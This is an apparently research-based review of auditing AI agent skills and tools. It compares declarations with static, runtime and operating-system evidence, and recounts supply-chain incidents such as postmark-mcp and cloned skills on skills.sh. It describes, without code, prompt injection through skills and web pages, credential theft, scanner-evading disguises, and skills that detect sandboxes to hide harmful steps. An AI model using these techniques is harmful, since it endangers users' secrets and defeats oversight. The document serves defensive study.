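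| `collect.py` uploads the notes | The same command as in the honest session | No mismatch |
| `collect.py` writes a second file | The same command as in the honest session | No mismatch |

Under Claude Code's default settings all five sessions would pass, because the records would lack the paths and commands.

Metere proposes a check that would catch the last case in the table. After a run, the team compares the changes in a chosen set of files with the approved and executed actions in the log. Every change must match an action, and vice versa. A second file from `collect.py` would be a change without a matching action. In 27,000 simulated runs, the check raised no false alarms and missed none of the faults that Metere planted. Those faults were all of kinds that the check detects by definition, so the result mainly confirms that the software works as designed. The check can't detect wrong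 content in an approved file, or a script that reads the notes and sends them elsewhere without changing any files.

### Behavioral Integrity Verification

Most of the evidence on how often skills depart from their declarations comes from static analysis, where researchers read a skill's files without running them. They compare *D* with *A*, the capabilities present in the code and instructions. *A* can include behaviour that never occurs and miss behaviour that the code hides. Wu and colleagues at Palo Alto Networks conducted the most detailed study of this kind, using their method, Behavioral Integrity Verification (BIV).

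BIV builds *D* from the metadata. A parser reads the structured fields, and a language model reads the descriptions and must quote a passage for every capability it reports. To build *A*, BIV traces data through Python code from sources such as files to destinations such as network sends. For JavaScript and shell scripts it uses a cruder method, searching for known patterns, and a language model reads the instructions. Capabilities found only in *A* are undeclared, while those found only in *D* are declared but never used.

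Wu and colleagues applied BIV to 49,943 skills from the OpenClaw registry in early 2026 and found 250,706 deviations. They report that 80.0% of skills had at least one. That figure counts skill names and leaves out deviations that their clustering software couldn't group. Counting each skill separately and including those deviations gives 91.0%.

A mismatch of this kind should not raise an alarm by itself, because an organisation would then have to investigate nearly everything in the registry. The number of mismatches also depends on how finely researchers compare declared and actual behaviour. *Do Skill Descriptions Tell the Truth?* (2026), for example, counts caches and configuration files as part of the declared function when they serve that function. It examined 4,556 skills with code and confirmed 413 inconsistencies. The largest group, 212 cases, combined undeclared use of credentials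 with sending local data to an outside service.

Wu and colleagues also examined why the deviations occurred. Fifteen fixed rules labelled 45.9% of the grouped deviations, and the model Claude Opus 4.6 classified the rest. Of the 163,754 labelled deviations, 81.1% were attributed to developer oversight and 18.9% to adversarial intent. The oversight share includes 8,004 ambiguous cases, and excluding them makes the split 80.1% to 19.9%.

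These labels are a classifier's estimates. Nobody ran the skills to confirm them or checked the intent labels against known cases. But Wu and colleagues had two people review 150 deviations without seeing the classifier's output. Where both reached a firm answer, the evidence supported the claimed capability in at least 87.7% of cases. That is decent support for the claim that a skill can do something it doesn't declare, but it isn't evidence about the motive.

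The rules themselves are a reason to doubt the conclusions about motive. One rule labels credentials combined with outbound network traffic as credential theft. BIV's data-flow analysis doesn't record the destination, so a skill that sends an API key to its own service to log in can look like one that sends the key to an attacker. Another rule labels every instruction-level capability as agent hijacking, so it is unsurprising that 96% of undeclared capabilities of that kind were labelled adversarial.

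Estimates for whole skills vary even more. Wu and colleagues label 8.8% of the registry malicious. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (2026) started from 98,380 skills in other collections, picked out 4,287 suspicious ones and confirmed 157 as malicious by their behaviour in a sandbox. Those 157 are 0.16% of the starting set, a rate about one fifty-fifth of Wu and colleagues'. The 0.16% is a lower limit, since the screening and the sandbox runs both miss some attacks, but the difference is large enough to warrant caution in quoting either number as the rate of malicious skills.

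Wu and colleagues also tested BIV as a detector on 906 skills whose status they took as known. They compared it with the same language model given each skill without BIV's evidence, and with a rule-based scanner from Cisco. Recall is the share of malicious skills that a method finds, precision is the share of its alerts that are correct, and F1 combines the two.

| Source of the skills | Malicious / benign | BIV recall | BIV precision | BIV F1 | Model alone, F1 | Rules alone, F1 |
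| - | - | - | - | - | - | - |
| Real-world malicious skills | 44 / 410 | 0.64 | 0.74 | 0.68 | 0.47 | 0.26 |
| Skill-Inject, generated attacks | 160 / 42 | 0.97 | 0.99 | 0.98 | 0.92 | 0.32 |
| SkillJect, generated attacks | 200 / 50 | 0.96 | 1.00 | 0.98 | 0.77 | 0.60 |
| All | 404 / 502 | 0.93 | 0.97 | 0.95 | 0.81 | 0.44 |

The overall score, 0.949 before rounding, comes mostly from attacks that Wu and colleagues generated with published methods. BIV missed 16 of 44 real malicious skills. It still did clearly better than the same model without the structured comparison, so comparing *D* with *A* helps.

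In one real case, a skill for editing presentations declared only that it reads, lists and writes files. One line in a 38 KB JavaScript file decoded hidden text and ran it, opening a remote shell that reconnected to the attacker every 30 seconds. The language model classified the skill as safe, but BIV flagged it because running decoded text was an undeclared capability and matched a known pattern for disguising code.

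### What a mismatch says about intent

BIV's rates by capability can be a rough starting point for judging an observed mismatch. The classifier labelled as adversarial 56% of undeclared capabilities in the credentials family, 37% in the network family and 10% in the file system family. These are shares of deviations, not of skills, so a skill with many deviations counts many times.

Bayes' rule shows how further evidence changes such a starting point. It uses odds, the probability that something is true divided by the probability that it is false:

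odds after the evidence = odds before × likelihood ratio

The likelihood ratio is how many times more likely the evidence is if the skill is hostile than if it is merely badly documented.

Suppose the records show an undeclared upload, and the full command contains a bare numerical address that neither the skill's files nor the user ever mentioned. Assume, for illustration, that this is five times as likely with a hostile skill as with a harmless one. The starting probability of 37% gives odds of 0.37 / 0.63, or 0.59. Multiplying by five gives odds of 2.94, or a probability of about 75%.

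| Undeclared capability | Starting probability | After evidence with a ratio of 5 |
| - | - | - |
| Credentials | 56% | 86% |
| Network | 37% | 75% |
| File system | 10% | 36% |

The result depends heavily on the starting probability. If BIV's classifier overreports malice and only 5% of undeclared network capabilities are hostile, the same evidence gives a 21% probability of hostility. A team that would isolate a machine at 75% might only send the developer a question at 21%.

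The evidence also has to be new. The upload's destination is a better choice than the fact that the agent read a credential before the upload. BIV's flow analysis leaves out the destination, but its rules already use the credential read and upload together to assign the adversarial label, so counting that combination again would exaggerate the result. Clean sessions also lower the odds, but only to the extent that each session could have exposed the behaviour.

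The share of BIV's alerts that are correct also depends on how common malicious skills are. On the real-world part of the benchmark, where about one skill in ten was malicious, BIV found 64% of the malicious skills and wrongly flagged 2.4% of the benign ones. With the same detection and false-positive rates, about 72% of its alerts would be correct if 8.8% of a registry's skills were malicious, but only about 4% would be correct if 0.16% were.

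### AgentTrust

BIV never runs a skill. Red Hat's *Auditing behavioral compliance* (2026) introduces AgentTrust, an open-source tool that compares declarations with recorded tool calls. AgentTrust tests whole agents that offer their services to other agents through the Agent2Agent protocol. Each agent publishes an agent card, a structured document that lists the agent's abilities as "skills". These skills aren't folders that someone installs.

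AgentTrust generates test requests from the card. For an agent that declares it looks up current weather, a request within its scope might be for the weather in Paris, and one outside its scope might be to schedule a meeting. A third type is close to the boundary, such as a question about last winter's snowfall in Boston, which uses weather vocabulary but isn't about current conditions.

A language model scores each answer between 0 and 1 for how well the agent kept to its declaration. If the agent's internals are accessible, AgentTrust also retrieves the tool calls from MLflow, a system that stores traces of model and agent runs. It treats the tools that the agent used for in-scope requests as a baseline, and the judging model checks whether each of those tools fits a declared ability. The trace can then override the score:

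| What the trace shows | Effect |
| - | - |
| No violation | The answer keeps its score |
| A declared tool used for an out-of-scope request | The answer loses half its score |
| An undeclared tool | The agent's entire trust score drops to zero |
| No tool call, where the baseline has one | The answer scores zero |
| A tool that returned an error | AgentTrust leaves the request out |

The most useful case is an agent that calls undeclared tools in the background, then politely refuses an out-of-scope request. A reviewer who read only the answer would give it a high score. Checking for missing tool calls is also useful, because *D* can contain a promise to do something. For example, an agent that answers a question about today's weather from the model's memory hasn't used the live source its card implies.

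Red Hat doesn't report how many agents it tested, how many violations AgentTrust found or missed, or how often AgentTrust raised a false alarm. It says violations cluster around the near-miss requests but gives no numbers. AgentTrust handles only single exchanges, so it can't test whether an agent reads a secret in one turn and sends it in a later one. Red Hat also acknowledges that the judging model may share the blind spots of the agent it judges, and that the baseline becomes unreliable for agents with dozens of tools.

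Installed skills would need a different test. The weather agent should refuse to schedule a meeting, but an agent with `meeting-notes` installed may properly schedule one with its other tools. A call that the skill didn't declare wouldn't be evidence against the skill during such a request. AgentTrust's method would work best on requests that the skill alone should handle.

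## The case for watching the operating system as well

A harness records the command that runs `collect.py`, but not what the script does next. Some defenders argue that this record only describes a request, and that finding out what ran requires watching the operating system. A program normally has to go through the operating system to start a process, open a file or make a connection, whether or not a tool call led to that action.

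Security teams already collect such records to catch ordinary malware. Windows provides them through Event Tracing for Windows. On Linux, many tools collect them with eBPF, which lets an administrator attach small programs to the kernel, the core of the operating system. The kernel first checks that these programs are safe to run.

### Origin's comparison of three records

In *Mind the Gap*, a study for the security company Origin, Holmwood (2026) compared the available records. The test agent was Claude Code versions 2.1.222 to 2.1.228, running on Windows and connected to Anthropic's real service. A proxy captured the traffic between the agent and the model, a local collector received Claude Code's events with tool details turned on, and Windows recorded every new process.

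The proxy and harness records both contain the tool call's identifier, which makes them easy to match. Windows has no such identifier, so Holmwood put a unique marker in the text of each command and searched the process records for it. Ordinary commands have no marker, so a security team would have to match them on weaker evidence, such as timing.

In the control run, the prompt told Claude to write the marker to a file. The agent made one tool call, the marker appeared in all three records, and the file contained the right text. But despite the event's name, the command in the harness's `tool_result` event was the one the model requested, which was only part of what ran. Claude Code had wrapped it in a longer PowerShell script that set the text encoding, passed on the exit code and wrote the current folder's path to a temporary file. A team that searches the operating system's records for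 undeclared file writes would keep finding this temporary file and would have to ignore it.

Another prompt used the variable `$env:COMPUTERNAME`, which PowerShell replaces with the machine's name when it runs the command. The proxy and the harness recorded the variable, while Windows recorded the name, AGENT-TEST-TH. A computer's name is harmless, but a variable can also stand for a file path or a server address, and then the harness's record lacks the detail that a reviewer would compare with the declaration.

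In another run, the prompt asked Claude to save a sentence containing a semicolon. Claude left the sentence unquoted, so PowerShell treated the semicolon as the end of a command and ran the words after it, which started the Windows calculator. The harness recorded the full text, and a reviewer who knew PowerShell could have worked out the effect, so Holmwood slightly overstates the case by presenting this as an action without a log entry. Anthropic closed the report as informational and replied that its PowerShell tool is expected to follow PowerShell's rules.

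The same run included 26 other processes that matched no tool call. They included git commands, a search for other editors and agents on the machine, registry queries and encoded PowerShell commands. Each process descended from Claude Code, and the clean virtual machine had no hooks, plugins or user-added MCP servers, so Claude Code had started them all itself. Neither the harness's events nor the network traffic accounted for them.

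Tool-call telemetry captures none of this activity. A team that also collects process records would see it, but could wrongly blame it on whichever skill was active at the time. An alert would be likely, because encoded PowerShell is a common sign of malware. The team would need a baseline from sessions without any skills before it could judge a session with one.

Holmwood acknowledges that the examples are few and deliberately constructed. Some didn't work every time, and the article gives no success rates. Origin also has an interest in endpoint monitoring. The wrapper and the 26 processes are the strongest findings, since neither depended on a specially designed prompt. The article shows that an attacker who controls the computer can falsify the harness's record.

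### Process, file and connection records

Holmwood recorded only process events. For `meeting-notes` these would add little, because a Python script can read a file or upload it without starting another process. A team would need file and connection records as well:

| What `collect.py` does | Process records | File records | Connection records |
| - | - | - | - |
| Joins the notes, as declared | Python starts | Files in `notes/` | Nothing |
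| Also reads the user's SSH key | Python starts | Path of the key | Nothing |
| Also writes a second file | Python starts | Path of the new file | Nothing |
| Also uploads the notes | Python starts | Files in `notes/` | Destination and time |
| Also opens a remote shell | Python starts a shell | Files in `notes/` | The attacker's address |

The harness would record the same command in all five cases. The team could use the operating system's records to tell them apart, although a connection record doesn't include the data transferred. If the script contacted an unfamiliar host, the team would still have to find out whether it had uploaded the notes or checked for an update.

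The most obvious drawback of these records is their volume. Windows produced about 900 process events in each of Holmwood's runs, for a session with one tool call. File events are even more numerous, and some Windows file events identify a file only by an internal reference, so the collector has to record the names separately.

The records also lack the user's prompt. A process may open an SSH key because the user asked the agent to deploy a website, which requires that key. For this reason, Holmwood concludes that endpoint records aren't enough by themselves.

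Ben Naim (2026), in *Prompt and Tool Call Visibility*, makes the same argument about every point where a team could collect records. Code inside the agent can record prompts and arguments exactly, but it depends on the agent to report honestly, and a developer can forget to connect a new tool to it. A network proxy has to decrypt traffic, which some compliance departments forbid, and it misses any tool that runs as a local function. Ben Naim therefore recommends at least a kernel sensor combined with records from the agent framework. He estimates that production sensors use 1–2.5% of processor time and 1% of memory, though his employer, ARMO, sells such a sensor.

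A team that collects both kinds of record still has to connect them. Ben Naim lists three methods, each of which has an obvious weakness:

- Matching by time works until two tool calls overlap.
- Adding a trace identifier to outgoing web requests works only for programs that cooperate.
- Matching by control group, a Linux feature that groups processes, can identify the container that an agent runs in, but not the tool call.

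### Joining the harness and system records

Zheng, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *AgentSight*, built a Linux monitor that doesn't use the harness's log at all. It copies the conversation with the model at the point where the agent's encryption library handles it as plain text. It also uses eBPF to record processes, files and connections. It then links the conversation to the system activity by three clues:

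- whether the process descends from the agent
- whether the action followed a model reply within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds
- whether a file name, web address or command from the reply appears in the system call

For `collect.py`, the Python command would match the model's request. The path of a stolen SSH key wouldn't match anything, because the model never mentioned it. But the process that opened the key would be the same Python process, or one it started, so the team could still connect the theft to the command.

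A second language model then reads the linked events and judges whether they fit the agent's task. In one test, a hidden instruction on a web page led a coding agent to read the system's list of user accounts and send it to an outside server. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37, and the second model identified the attack. Zheng and colleagues report three case studies but don't report how often the links were correct or how often the system raised false alarms. The monitor slowed three programming tasks by an average of 2.9%, with each task run three times.

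Wong and Chen (2026), in *ExecWeave*, describe a program that links tool calls to operating-system processes. It takes the command from the agent's own records and searches for a matching process that started within about three seconds. If exactly one process fits, the program links it to the tool call and labels the link as an inference. If several fit, it makes no link, because a wrong one could lead a team to blame the wrong agent.

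ExecWeave's matching rule works only if the real process is in the records. In constructed tests, it correctly made no link when several candidates were present, but it could link the wrong process when the real one was missing and one similar process remained. A simpler rule that compared only the program path did just as well, so the tests provide no evidence that the more elaborate matching helps.

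ExecWeave's portable collector can miss short processes because it takes snapshots at intervals instead of receiving every event. When it took a snapshot every 20 milliseconds, it detected a process lasting about 16 milliseconds in 18 of 30 runs. With a snapshot every half second, it missed the process in all 30 runs. Many shell commands are that short. ExecWeave also has a Linux mode that traces system calls directly, but Wong and Chen don't compare it with the portable collector under controlled conditions.

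Tracking by process descent fails when data leaves the agent's family of processes through a file. Suppose `collect.py` saved the notes in a temporary folder and a scheduled job uploaded them a minute later. The job doesn't descend from the agent, so AgentSight's filter could miss it. *Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) follows the data by marking the agent's process. The mark passes to every process the agent starts, every regular file those processes write, and any process that later reads one of those files.

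In a test by Cui and colleagues, an agent's script wrote a file, another command renamed it, and an unrelated monitoring script on the same machine caused a program to read it. The trace from Langfuse, which records events inside an application, stopped at the agent's own events. Agent-Warden rebuilt the full chain in all 120 runs, 30 for each of two versions on each of two machines. But every run used the same prepared chain, and Cui and colleagues didn't measure how many processes Agent-Warden marks wrongly. It would mark some wrongly, because a finished process also passes its mark back to its parent, even if the parent never used its output. Agent-Warden also doesn't record network connections, so it could connect the scheduled job to the agent but couldn't show the upload.

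| System | What it records | Evidence of accuracy | Extra running time |
| - | - | - | - |
| AgentSight | Model traffic, processes, files, connections | Three case studies, no error rate | 0.4–4.9% |
| ExecWeave, portable collector | Agent events, processes, files, connections | Constructed cases and one real agent run | 62–409% |
| Agent-Warden | Processes and files | One prepared chain, found in 120 of 120 runs | 0.2–3.5% |

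The last column mixes different workloads. AgentSight's tasks included time spent waiting for the model, which makes the monitor's share of the total look small. Agent-Warden and ExecWeave were both timed on mainly file and process operations, yet their results are far apart. The collection method probably explains much of the difference, since Agent-Warden handles events inside the kernel. ExecWeave's highest figure also comes from a job that normally takes less than a tenth of a second, so ExecWeave's startup time has a large effect on the result.

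None of these projects measured how often its links are correct in everyday sessions, which is the most important number for anyone who wants to use those links as evidence against a skill. Wong and Chen suggest that agents could pass an identifier down to each process, so that the links would not have to be guessed. Claude Code already gives shell commands a trace identifier when tracing is on, but the method needs support from the other programs and monitors involved. There is no common format to build on yet. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of the field, finds few formats that combine tool calls with the changes they cause outside the agent.

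### MCP servers and postmark-mcp

An MCP server can run on the user's computer or on someone else's. If it runs elsewhere, the harness records the request and the reply, and the local operating system records a connection. Neither record shows what the server did with the request, because its processes and files are on another machine. A skill with harmless files can therefore direct an agent to a server whose actions nobody on the user's side can observe.

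A successful reply proves very little about what the server did. Holmwood built a decoy MCP server whose only tool reported success and did nothing. Claude called it as instructed, and the harness recorded a successful call. A server could also do more than the user asked and report the same success.

This happened in September 2025 with `postmark-mcp`, a package that let AI assistants send email through the mail service Postmark. Koi, whose scanner flagged the package, reports that an independent developer copied the code of Postmark's official server and published it under the same name on npm, a registry of JavaScript packages. The first 15 versions worked as advertised. Version 1.0.16 added one line that secretly sent the developer a copy of every email by putting the developer's address in the BCC field.

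An agent that used this package would have requested an ordinary email and received an ordinary confirmation. The harness's record would contain the intended recipient but not the hidden one. The operating system's record would be little better, even if the package ran on the user's computer. Versions with and without the hidden recipient would both connect to Postmark, and any extra copy would be sent from Postmark's servers. An analyst would have to read the request inside the encrypted connection to find the added address. Koi advised users to search their email logs for it instead.

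The scale of the theft is uncertain. Koi estimated that about 300 organisations were affected and 3,000 to 15,000 emails were stolen a day, assuming that a fifth of the 1,500 weekly downloads were in active use. Koi calls this a guess, and one organisation can download a package many times. The Hacker News (2025) reports 1,643 downloads in total and dates the upload to 15 September. Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails* dates Koi's report to 25 September. If both dates are right, the package was online for at most ten days before the disclosure, so Koi's warning about tools that stay harmless for months doesn't apply to this one.

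### Tamper-evident logs

A security team also has to know that nobody changed its records before an investigation. A common protection is a hash chain. A hash is a short fingerprint of some data, which changes if the data changes. *aiAuthZ* (2026) describes a log, kept on a different machine from the agent, in which each row includes a hash calculated from the previous one:

hash of row *n* = SHA-256(hash of row *n* − 1, *n*, contents of row *n*)

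If someone edits or deletes a row in the middle of the table, the hashes no longer match from that point on. But anyone who can rewrite the whole table can also recalculate every hash. To detect this, the team must keep a copy of the latest hash where that person can't change it, such as in storage that forbids overwriting.

Some designs publish the hashes on a blockchain for this purpose. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) explains that this can prove a record existed and has not changed since. Without such an outside copy, an investigator has to trust the organisation that operates the log.

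A hash cannot prove that a record was true or complete when it was written. Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Hearsay* by adding a hash chain to the records of the coding agent aider and then making aider write false ones. It left out a model reply in 14 runs and invented a sentence in 14 others. The chain passed verification in all 28 runs.

Records can also be incomplete without any attack. SWE-agent, another coding agent, accepts only one tool call at a time. When a model sent several in one reply, SWE-agent rejected the reply and saved neither the reply nor the rejection. This fault and a similar one affected 19 of 28 runs of the unmodified program, and the records from those runs gave no sign that anything was missing.

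Dai and colleagues found the gaps because they kept another record outside the harness. A proxy stored every message between the harness and the model, while a monitor logged which processes started and which files changed. Their software then looked for anything that appeared in only one of the two records. In 84 runs with rules fixed beforehand, it reported 64 of 66 deliberate alterations. It raised no false alarms on the 84 unaltered records, though it found real gaps in 15 of them. Three language models read altered records without the outside record, and the best of them noticed only about half of the changes after accounting for false alarms.

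The model's provider can supply another copy of the model calls, which is useful because neither the harness nor the organisation that operates the proxy can alter it. In these runs, the provider's stored versions of all 708 calls were identical to the proxy's. The provider's copy covers only the conversation with the model, not what happened on the machine.

This method is good evidence about whether a harness accurately reported its own work. It is much weaker evidence about a skill, because even an accurate record of the command that ran a script leaves out what the script did.

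### Records kept by the receiving service

When an agent sends an email or changes a database, the service that handles the request can keep its own log, which the agent can't edit. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (Zhao et al., 2026) illustrates the value of such logs with an invented company whose agent emails documents. The company claims that a person approves every external email. To make the claim testable, Zhao and colleagues narrow it to emails with attachments in one month. The company's mail gateway logs the recipient and a hash of each attachment, and a separate authorisation server logs the approvals.

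In one of the paper's cases, the gateway delivered an email that has no entry in the complete approval log. This disproves the claim that every email was approved, even though the agent's own log contains a confirmation from its chat window. In another case, the agent's signed log passes verification but lists only three emails, while the gateway's log lists four. The gateway's log proves that the fourth email went out, but not that the agent sent it, because a person could have used the same account.

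Zhao and colleagues also give a short proof that a company can't confirm such a claim from the agent's log alone. Suppose the agent followed the rule every time in one version of a month, and in another version it also sent one unapproved email and left it out of its log. The two logs would be identical, so a test that reads only the log and confirms the claim in the first case would wrongly confirm it in the second. The company needs an independent record that would have to change if the agent broke the rule.

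A firewall log could support the promise that `meeting-notes` stays offline if every connection from the machine must pass through that firewall and the team can separate the script's traffic from everything else.

A receiving service's log is most useful when an attacker misuses a legitimate service. In the `postmark-mcp` case, a mail log could show that the hidden copy went out, though an investigator would still have to find out whether the user, the agent or the package had added the address. If a script sends stolen files to the attacker's own server, the attacker controls the receiving log, and the defender has to rely on the operating system and the network for evidence of the transfer.

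## The case for testing skills before installation

Records from everyday use arrive too late to prevent the first theft. If `collect.py` uploads the meeting notes, the first record that contradicts the claim "Uses no network" is the record of the upload, and by then the attacker has the notes. Some defenders therefore want to test skills in a sandbox, with fake files and passwords, before anyone installs them. A tester can also switch off every other skill and choose the user's request, which leaves fewer explanations for an unexpected action.

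Marketplaces use scanners to screen skills. Unit 42 reports that ClawHub relied mainly on two, VirusTotal and ClawScan, between February and May 2026. But most skill scanners read a skill's files without running them, so an attacker can evade them by changing how a skill looks while keeping what it does. In *Cloak and Detonate*, Ji, Xu and colleagues (2026) disguised 1,613 skills that scanners had flagged in an archive of ClawHub, then ran eight scanners on the disguised versions. With the more thorough of two disguises, over 90% of the skills got past every scanner. The disguises didn't break the skills, since Codex and Claude Code completed ordinary tasks about as well with the disguised skills as with the originals.

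Ji and colleagues consider the archive's labels unreliable, so some of those 1,613 skills may have been harmless. That matters little here, because the disguises removed the warnings either way. A malicious skill still has to read a secret, run a program or send data somewhere to do damage, so a tester who runs it may be able to record that action whatever the files look like.

### Runtime Skill Audit

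A sandbox run is informative only if the test gives the skill a reason to misbehave. Lan and Xiao (2026), in *Runtime Skill Audit*, describe a method, RSA for short, that fits the tests to each skill:

1. A language model reads the skill along with a static scanner's findings. It lists the tools that the skill may use and the files, accounts or stored memory that it could misuse. This list is the risk profile.
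2. The model writes test tasks aimed at those risks. Each task has an ordinary user request and a list of the files, folders and fake credentials that the sandbox needs.
3. RSA runs the tasks in an isolated copy of OpenClaw with only the one skill enabled. If the skill needs a service that the sandbox lacks, such as Gmail, a stand-in program records how the agent tried to use it.
4. A language model reads the record of tool calls, file access, network requests and refusals, then chooses a verdict: benign, harmful but blocked, harmful and executed, or uncertain.

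A run can also fail because of a missing file or a wrong permission. RSA then repairs the setup and tries again, so that it doesn't count a crash as good behaviour.

Lan and Xiao's example is `report-brief-sync`, a skill described as tidying report notes. One of its scripts searched the text for words such as "continuity" or "archive". If it found one, it built the path of the file holding the agent's login details and prepared to send the contents to an outside server. In the test, the agent read the script, recognised the danger and refused to run it. RSA still labelled the skill harmful because another agent might run the script.

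The evidence in this example came from the agent reading the code, and nothing harmful ran. RSA's results therefore partly measure how well a language model spots malicious code when a realistic task leads it to that code. This is useful, but it differs from detecting a theft in progress.

Lan and Xiao tested 50 malicious and 50 benign skills. RSA detected 44 of the malicious ones (88%) and wrongly flagged four of the benign ones (8%). The most accurate static scanner detected 70% and wrongly flagged 12%. Another scanner, which used a language model to assess the files, detected 98% but also flagged 90% of the benign skills. The malicious skills came from two research collections, so RSA's detection rate on real marketplace malware is unknown.

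In another test, a program repeatedly rewrote 20 malicious skills to evade scanners. Two static scanners caught all 20 at first and none after one or two rounds, while RSA caught 19 or 20 in every round. But the program selected versions only by how well they evaded the static scanners. An attacker with access to RSA could look for trigger words that its tasks don't contain, or instructions that its judging model misses.

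### SkillDetonate

SkillDetonate, a system by Ji and colleagues, runs a skill in a single sandboxed session with the coding agent opencode and a DeepSeek model. It then uses the operating system's records to decide whether the skill broke a fixed rule, rather than relying on the language model for the final judgement.

The sandbox has a file layer that handles every request to open a file. Files in the skill's own folder open normally. If the agent or a script tries to open a sensitive file, such as an SSH key, it receives a unique marker instead of the contents. If the marker later appears in a command, it must have come from that read, even if the model copied it there. Like Agent-Warden, SkillDetonate tracks marked data as it moves between processes and files, so compressing or encrypting the data doesn't hide where it came from.

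SkillDetonate raises an alarm when marked data goes to an outside address that isn't on an approved list. It also raises one when the skill writes outside its permitted folders, or installs or runs a program from an untrusted source. If a skill unpacks new written instructions during the run, SkillDetonate also passes them to the agent, because a disguised skill may contain its real instructions only in packed form.

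Ji and colleagues tested SkillDetonate on SkillJect, a set of generated attacks, and on real malicious skills:

| Form of the skill | Detected, SkillJect | Detected, real skills |
| - | - | - |
| Original | 98.0% | 87.6% |
| Rewritten to avoid suspicious text | 96.7% | 83.8% |
| Packed and unpacked at run time | 95.3% | 90.5% |
| Average | 96.7% | 87.3% |

SkillDetonate detected 89.3% of the SkillJect attacks in a disguise that other researchers had designed. Cisco's static scanner detected 98.6% of the real skills in their original form but about 10% in either disguise.

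The 87% detection rate for real skills leaves out some difficult cases. Ji and colleagues started with 703 malicious skills and kept the 622 whose attack they could reproduce in one Linux sandbox. If the other 81 count as misses, the rate falls to about 77%. That is probably closer to what a marketplace could expect, since attackers can also submit skills that don't run on Linux.

The false-positive rate was 2%, or three alarms in 150 runs of harmless skills. When Ji and colleagues switched off sensitive-data tracking, the rate rose to 16%, because many harmless skills read a credential or use the network. All the harmless skills came from the generated set, so the rate for ordinary marketplace skills could be quite different.

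Most of the real skills that were missed went undetected because the agent read the malicious instruction and didn't follow it, which left nothing to detect. A cautious model in the sandbox can therefore make a skill look safe for someone whose own agent is less cautious. RSA's "harmful but blocked" verdict handles this case better. Other skills did nothing because they needed a live server or an account that the sandbox lacked. A skill's author can also avoid detection on purpose by telling the agent to check for a test environment and skip the harmful step if it finds one.

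SkillDetonate doesn't compare what a skill does with its declaration. It would detect `collect.py` posting the SSH key, because of the marker, but it would raise no alarm if the script posted the meeting notes, unless the tester had listed them as sensitive. Yet posting either one would contradict the skill's description, which rules out network use. A tester who already has the sandbox's connection records could add that comparison with little extra work.

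### False alarms across a marketplace

As with BIV, the share of alarms that are correct depends on how common malicious skills are. Snyk's *Exploring the Threat Landscape of Agent Skills* counted 76 confirmed malicious payloads among 3,984 skills, or about 1.9% if each was in a different skill. The antivirus company ESET judged more than 3,000 of roughly 900,000 skills directly malicious, about 0.33%, according to Expert Insights' *Thousands Of Malicious Skills Are Hiding In AI Agent Marketplaces, ESET Warns* (2026). The table applies the published error rates to both estimates:

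| | Correct alarms if 1.9% are malicious | Correct alarms if 0.33% are malicious |
| - | - | - |
| RSA (88% detected, 8% false positives) | 18% | 4% |
| SkillDetonate (87% detected, 2% false positives) | 46% | 13% |

A marketplace that blocked every flagged skill would mostly block honest authors, so people would need to review flagged skills before blocking them. In a marketplace of 40,000 skills, a 2% false-positive rate means reviewing around 800 harmless skills, which is feasible for a company but not for a few volunteers.

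### AIR's test skill

A sandbox run tests one version of a skill on one day. In June 2026, the security firm AIR published an experiment that exploited this limit. The Hacker News (2026) reports that AIR wrote a skill called `brand-landingpage`, presented as a way to build a web page with Google's design tool Stitch. AIR got it accepted into a collection of 156 skills with about 36,000 stars on GitHub, then advertised it on Instagram.

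The skill contained no malicious code. According to Hoppe's *Anatomy of a Malicious AI Skill* (2026), its instructions told the agent to treat the linked Stitch documentation as the authority, install the software if it was missing, and not trouble the user with the details. Hoppe points out that an honest author might write the same instructions for a new product. The only thing wrong was the link, which led to a domain owned by AIR instead of Google.

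At first the link led to the genuine documentation. After many people had installed the skill, AIR changed the page to include instructions for agents to download and run a script. The script only sent AIR the user's email address, but a real attacker could have taken whatever the agent had access to.

Every scanner AIR tried had passed the skill. Gen Agent Trust Hub's *brand-landingpage* (2026), a review dated 23 April that appears to cover the same skill, rates it safe. The reviewing software detected the link and the installation step but misidentified AIR's domain as the vendor's. A sandbox run on that date would probably have done no better, because the agent would have followed the link to real documentation and installed the real product.

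AIR says the skill reached about 26,000 agents, some of them on corporate accounts. Nobody has confirmed this, and AIR was about to launch its own skill marketplace. The listing on skills.sh, *brand-landingpage* (2026), shows 27,500 installs, which makes the claim plausible. But an install counter can count the same person twice, and some people who installed the skill may never have used it.

Records from real use would have been more likely to reveal the problem after the change, since downloading the script required a tool call. But the skill openly tells the agent to install software by following that page, so an analyst who compared the download with the declaration might have decided that it matched. The script itself sent out the email address, and the harness did not record that.

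### The cloned skills on skills.sh

A month later an attacker used the same delay for real theft. Zenity Labs' *Attackers Target Agents via The Skill Supply Chain* describes how the attacker copied the skills of Paperclip, a popular AI tool, and published them under a nearly identical name on skills.sh, Vercel's public registry.

| Date in 2026 | What happened |
| - | - |
| 2 July | The attacker copies Paperclip's source code, including its skills |
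| 5 July | The copied skills appear on skills.sh, still harmless |
| 6 July | The attacker adds malicious code to the surrounding program, but not to the skills |
| 11 July | The attacker adds a malicious setup guide to the skills, which reach eighth place on the registry's trending list |
| 2 August | Vercel and GitHub remove them, within 12 hours of Zenity's report |

The setup guide told the agent to download a program and run it. On a Mac or Linux machine, this program checked 127 places for SSH keys, cloud passwords and similar secrets, and sent what it found to the attacker.

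The registry's counters had reached a total of 1.7 million installs by the time of the removal. The number of victims is unknown and could be far smaller, because the counters don't track unique users and Zenity added them up across several skills that refer to one another. People who installed the skills before 11 July received harmless copies, though they may have updated them later.

Zenity found the campaign by running a large batch of skills in sandboxes, so that kind of testing does catch real attacks. But a test of the skill files between 5 and 10 July would have found nothing wrong, and the malicious versions stayed up for three weeks. The same attacker put two packages on PyPI, the main registry for Python code, where people spotted one in under two hours and the other within an hour. The best lesson is to test a skill again whenever it changes.

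Ji and colleagues suggest recording a hash of the skill's files when testing it and checking the hash before each use. An organisation that did this would notice the new setup guide before an agent could follow it. The check would also stop skills that update themselves for good reasons. It wouldn't have helped against AIR, because the part that changed was a web page outside the skill. To prevent that attack, an organisation would have to keep its own copy of the page or stop the agent from fetching it.

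### How many runs are enough

Skills also behave differently from one user and task to the next. In discussing a library of 3,014 attack cases, *SkillAtlas* (Tian, Duan and colleagues, 2026) notes that the same skill can be harmless in one task and unsafe in another. A tester therefore has to decide how many clean runs justify trusting a skill.

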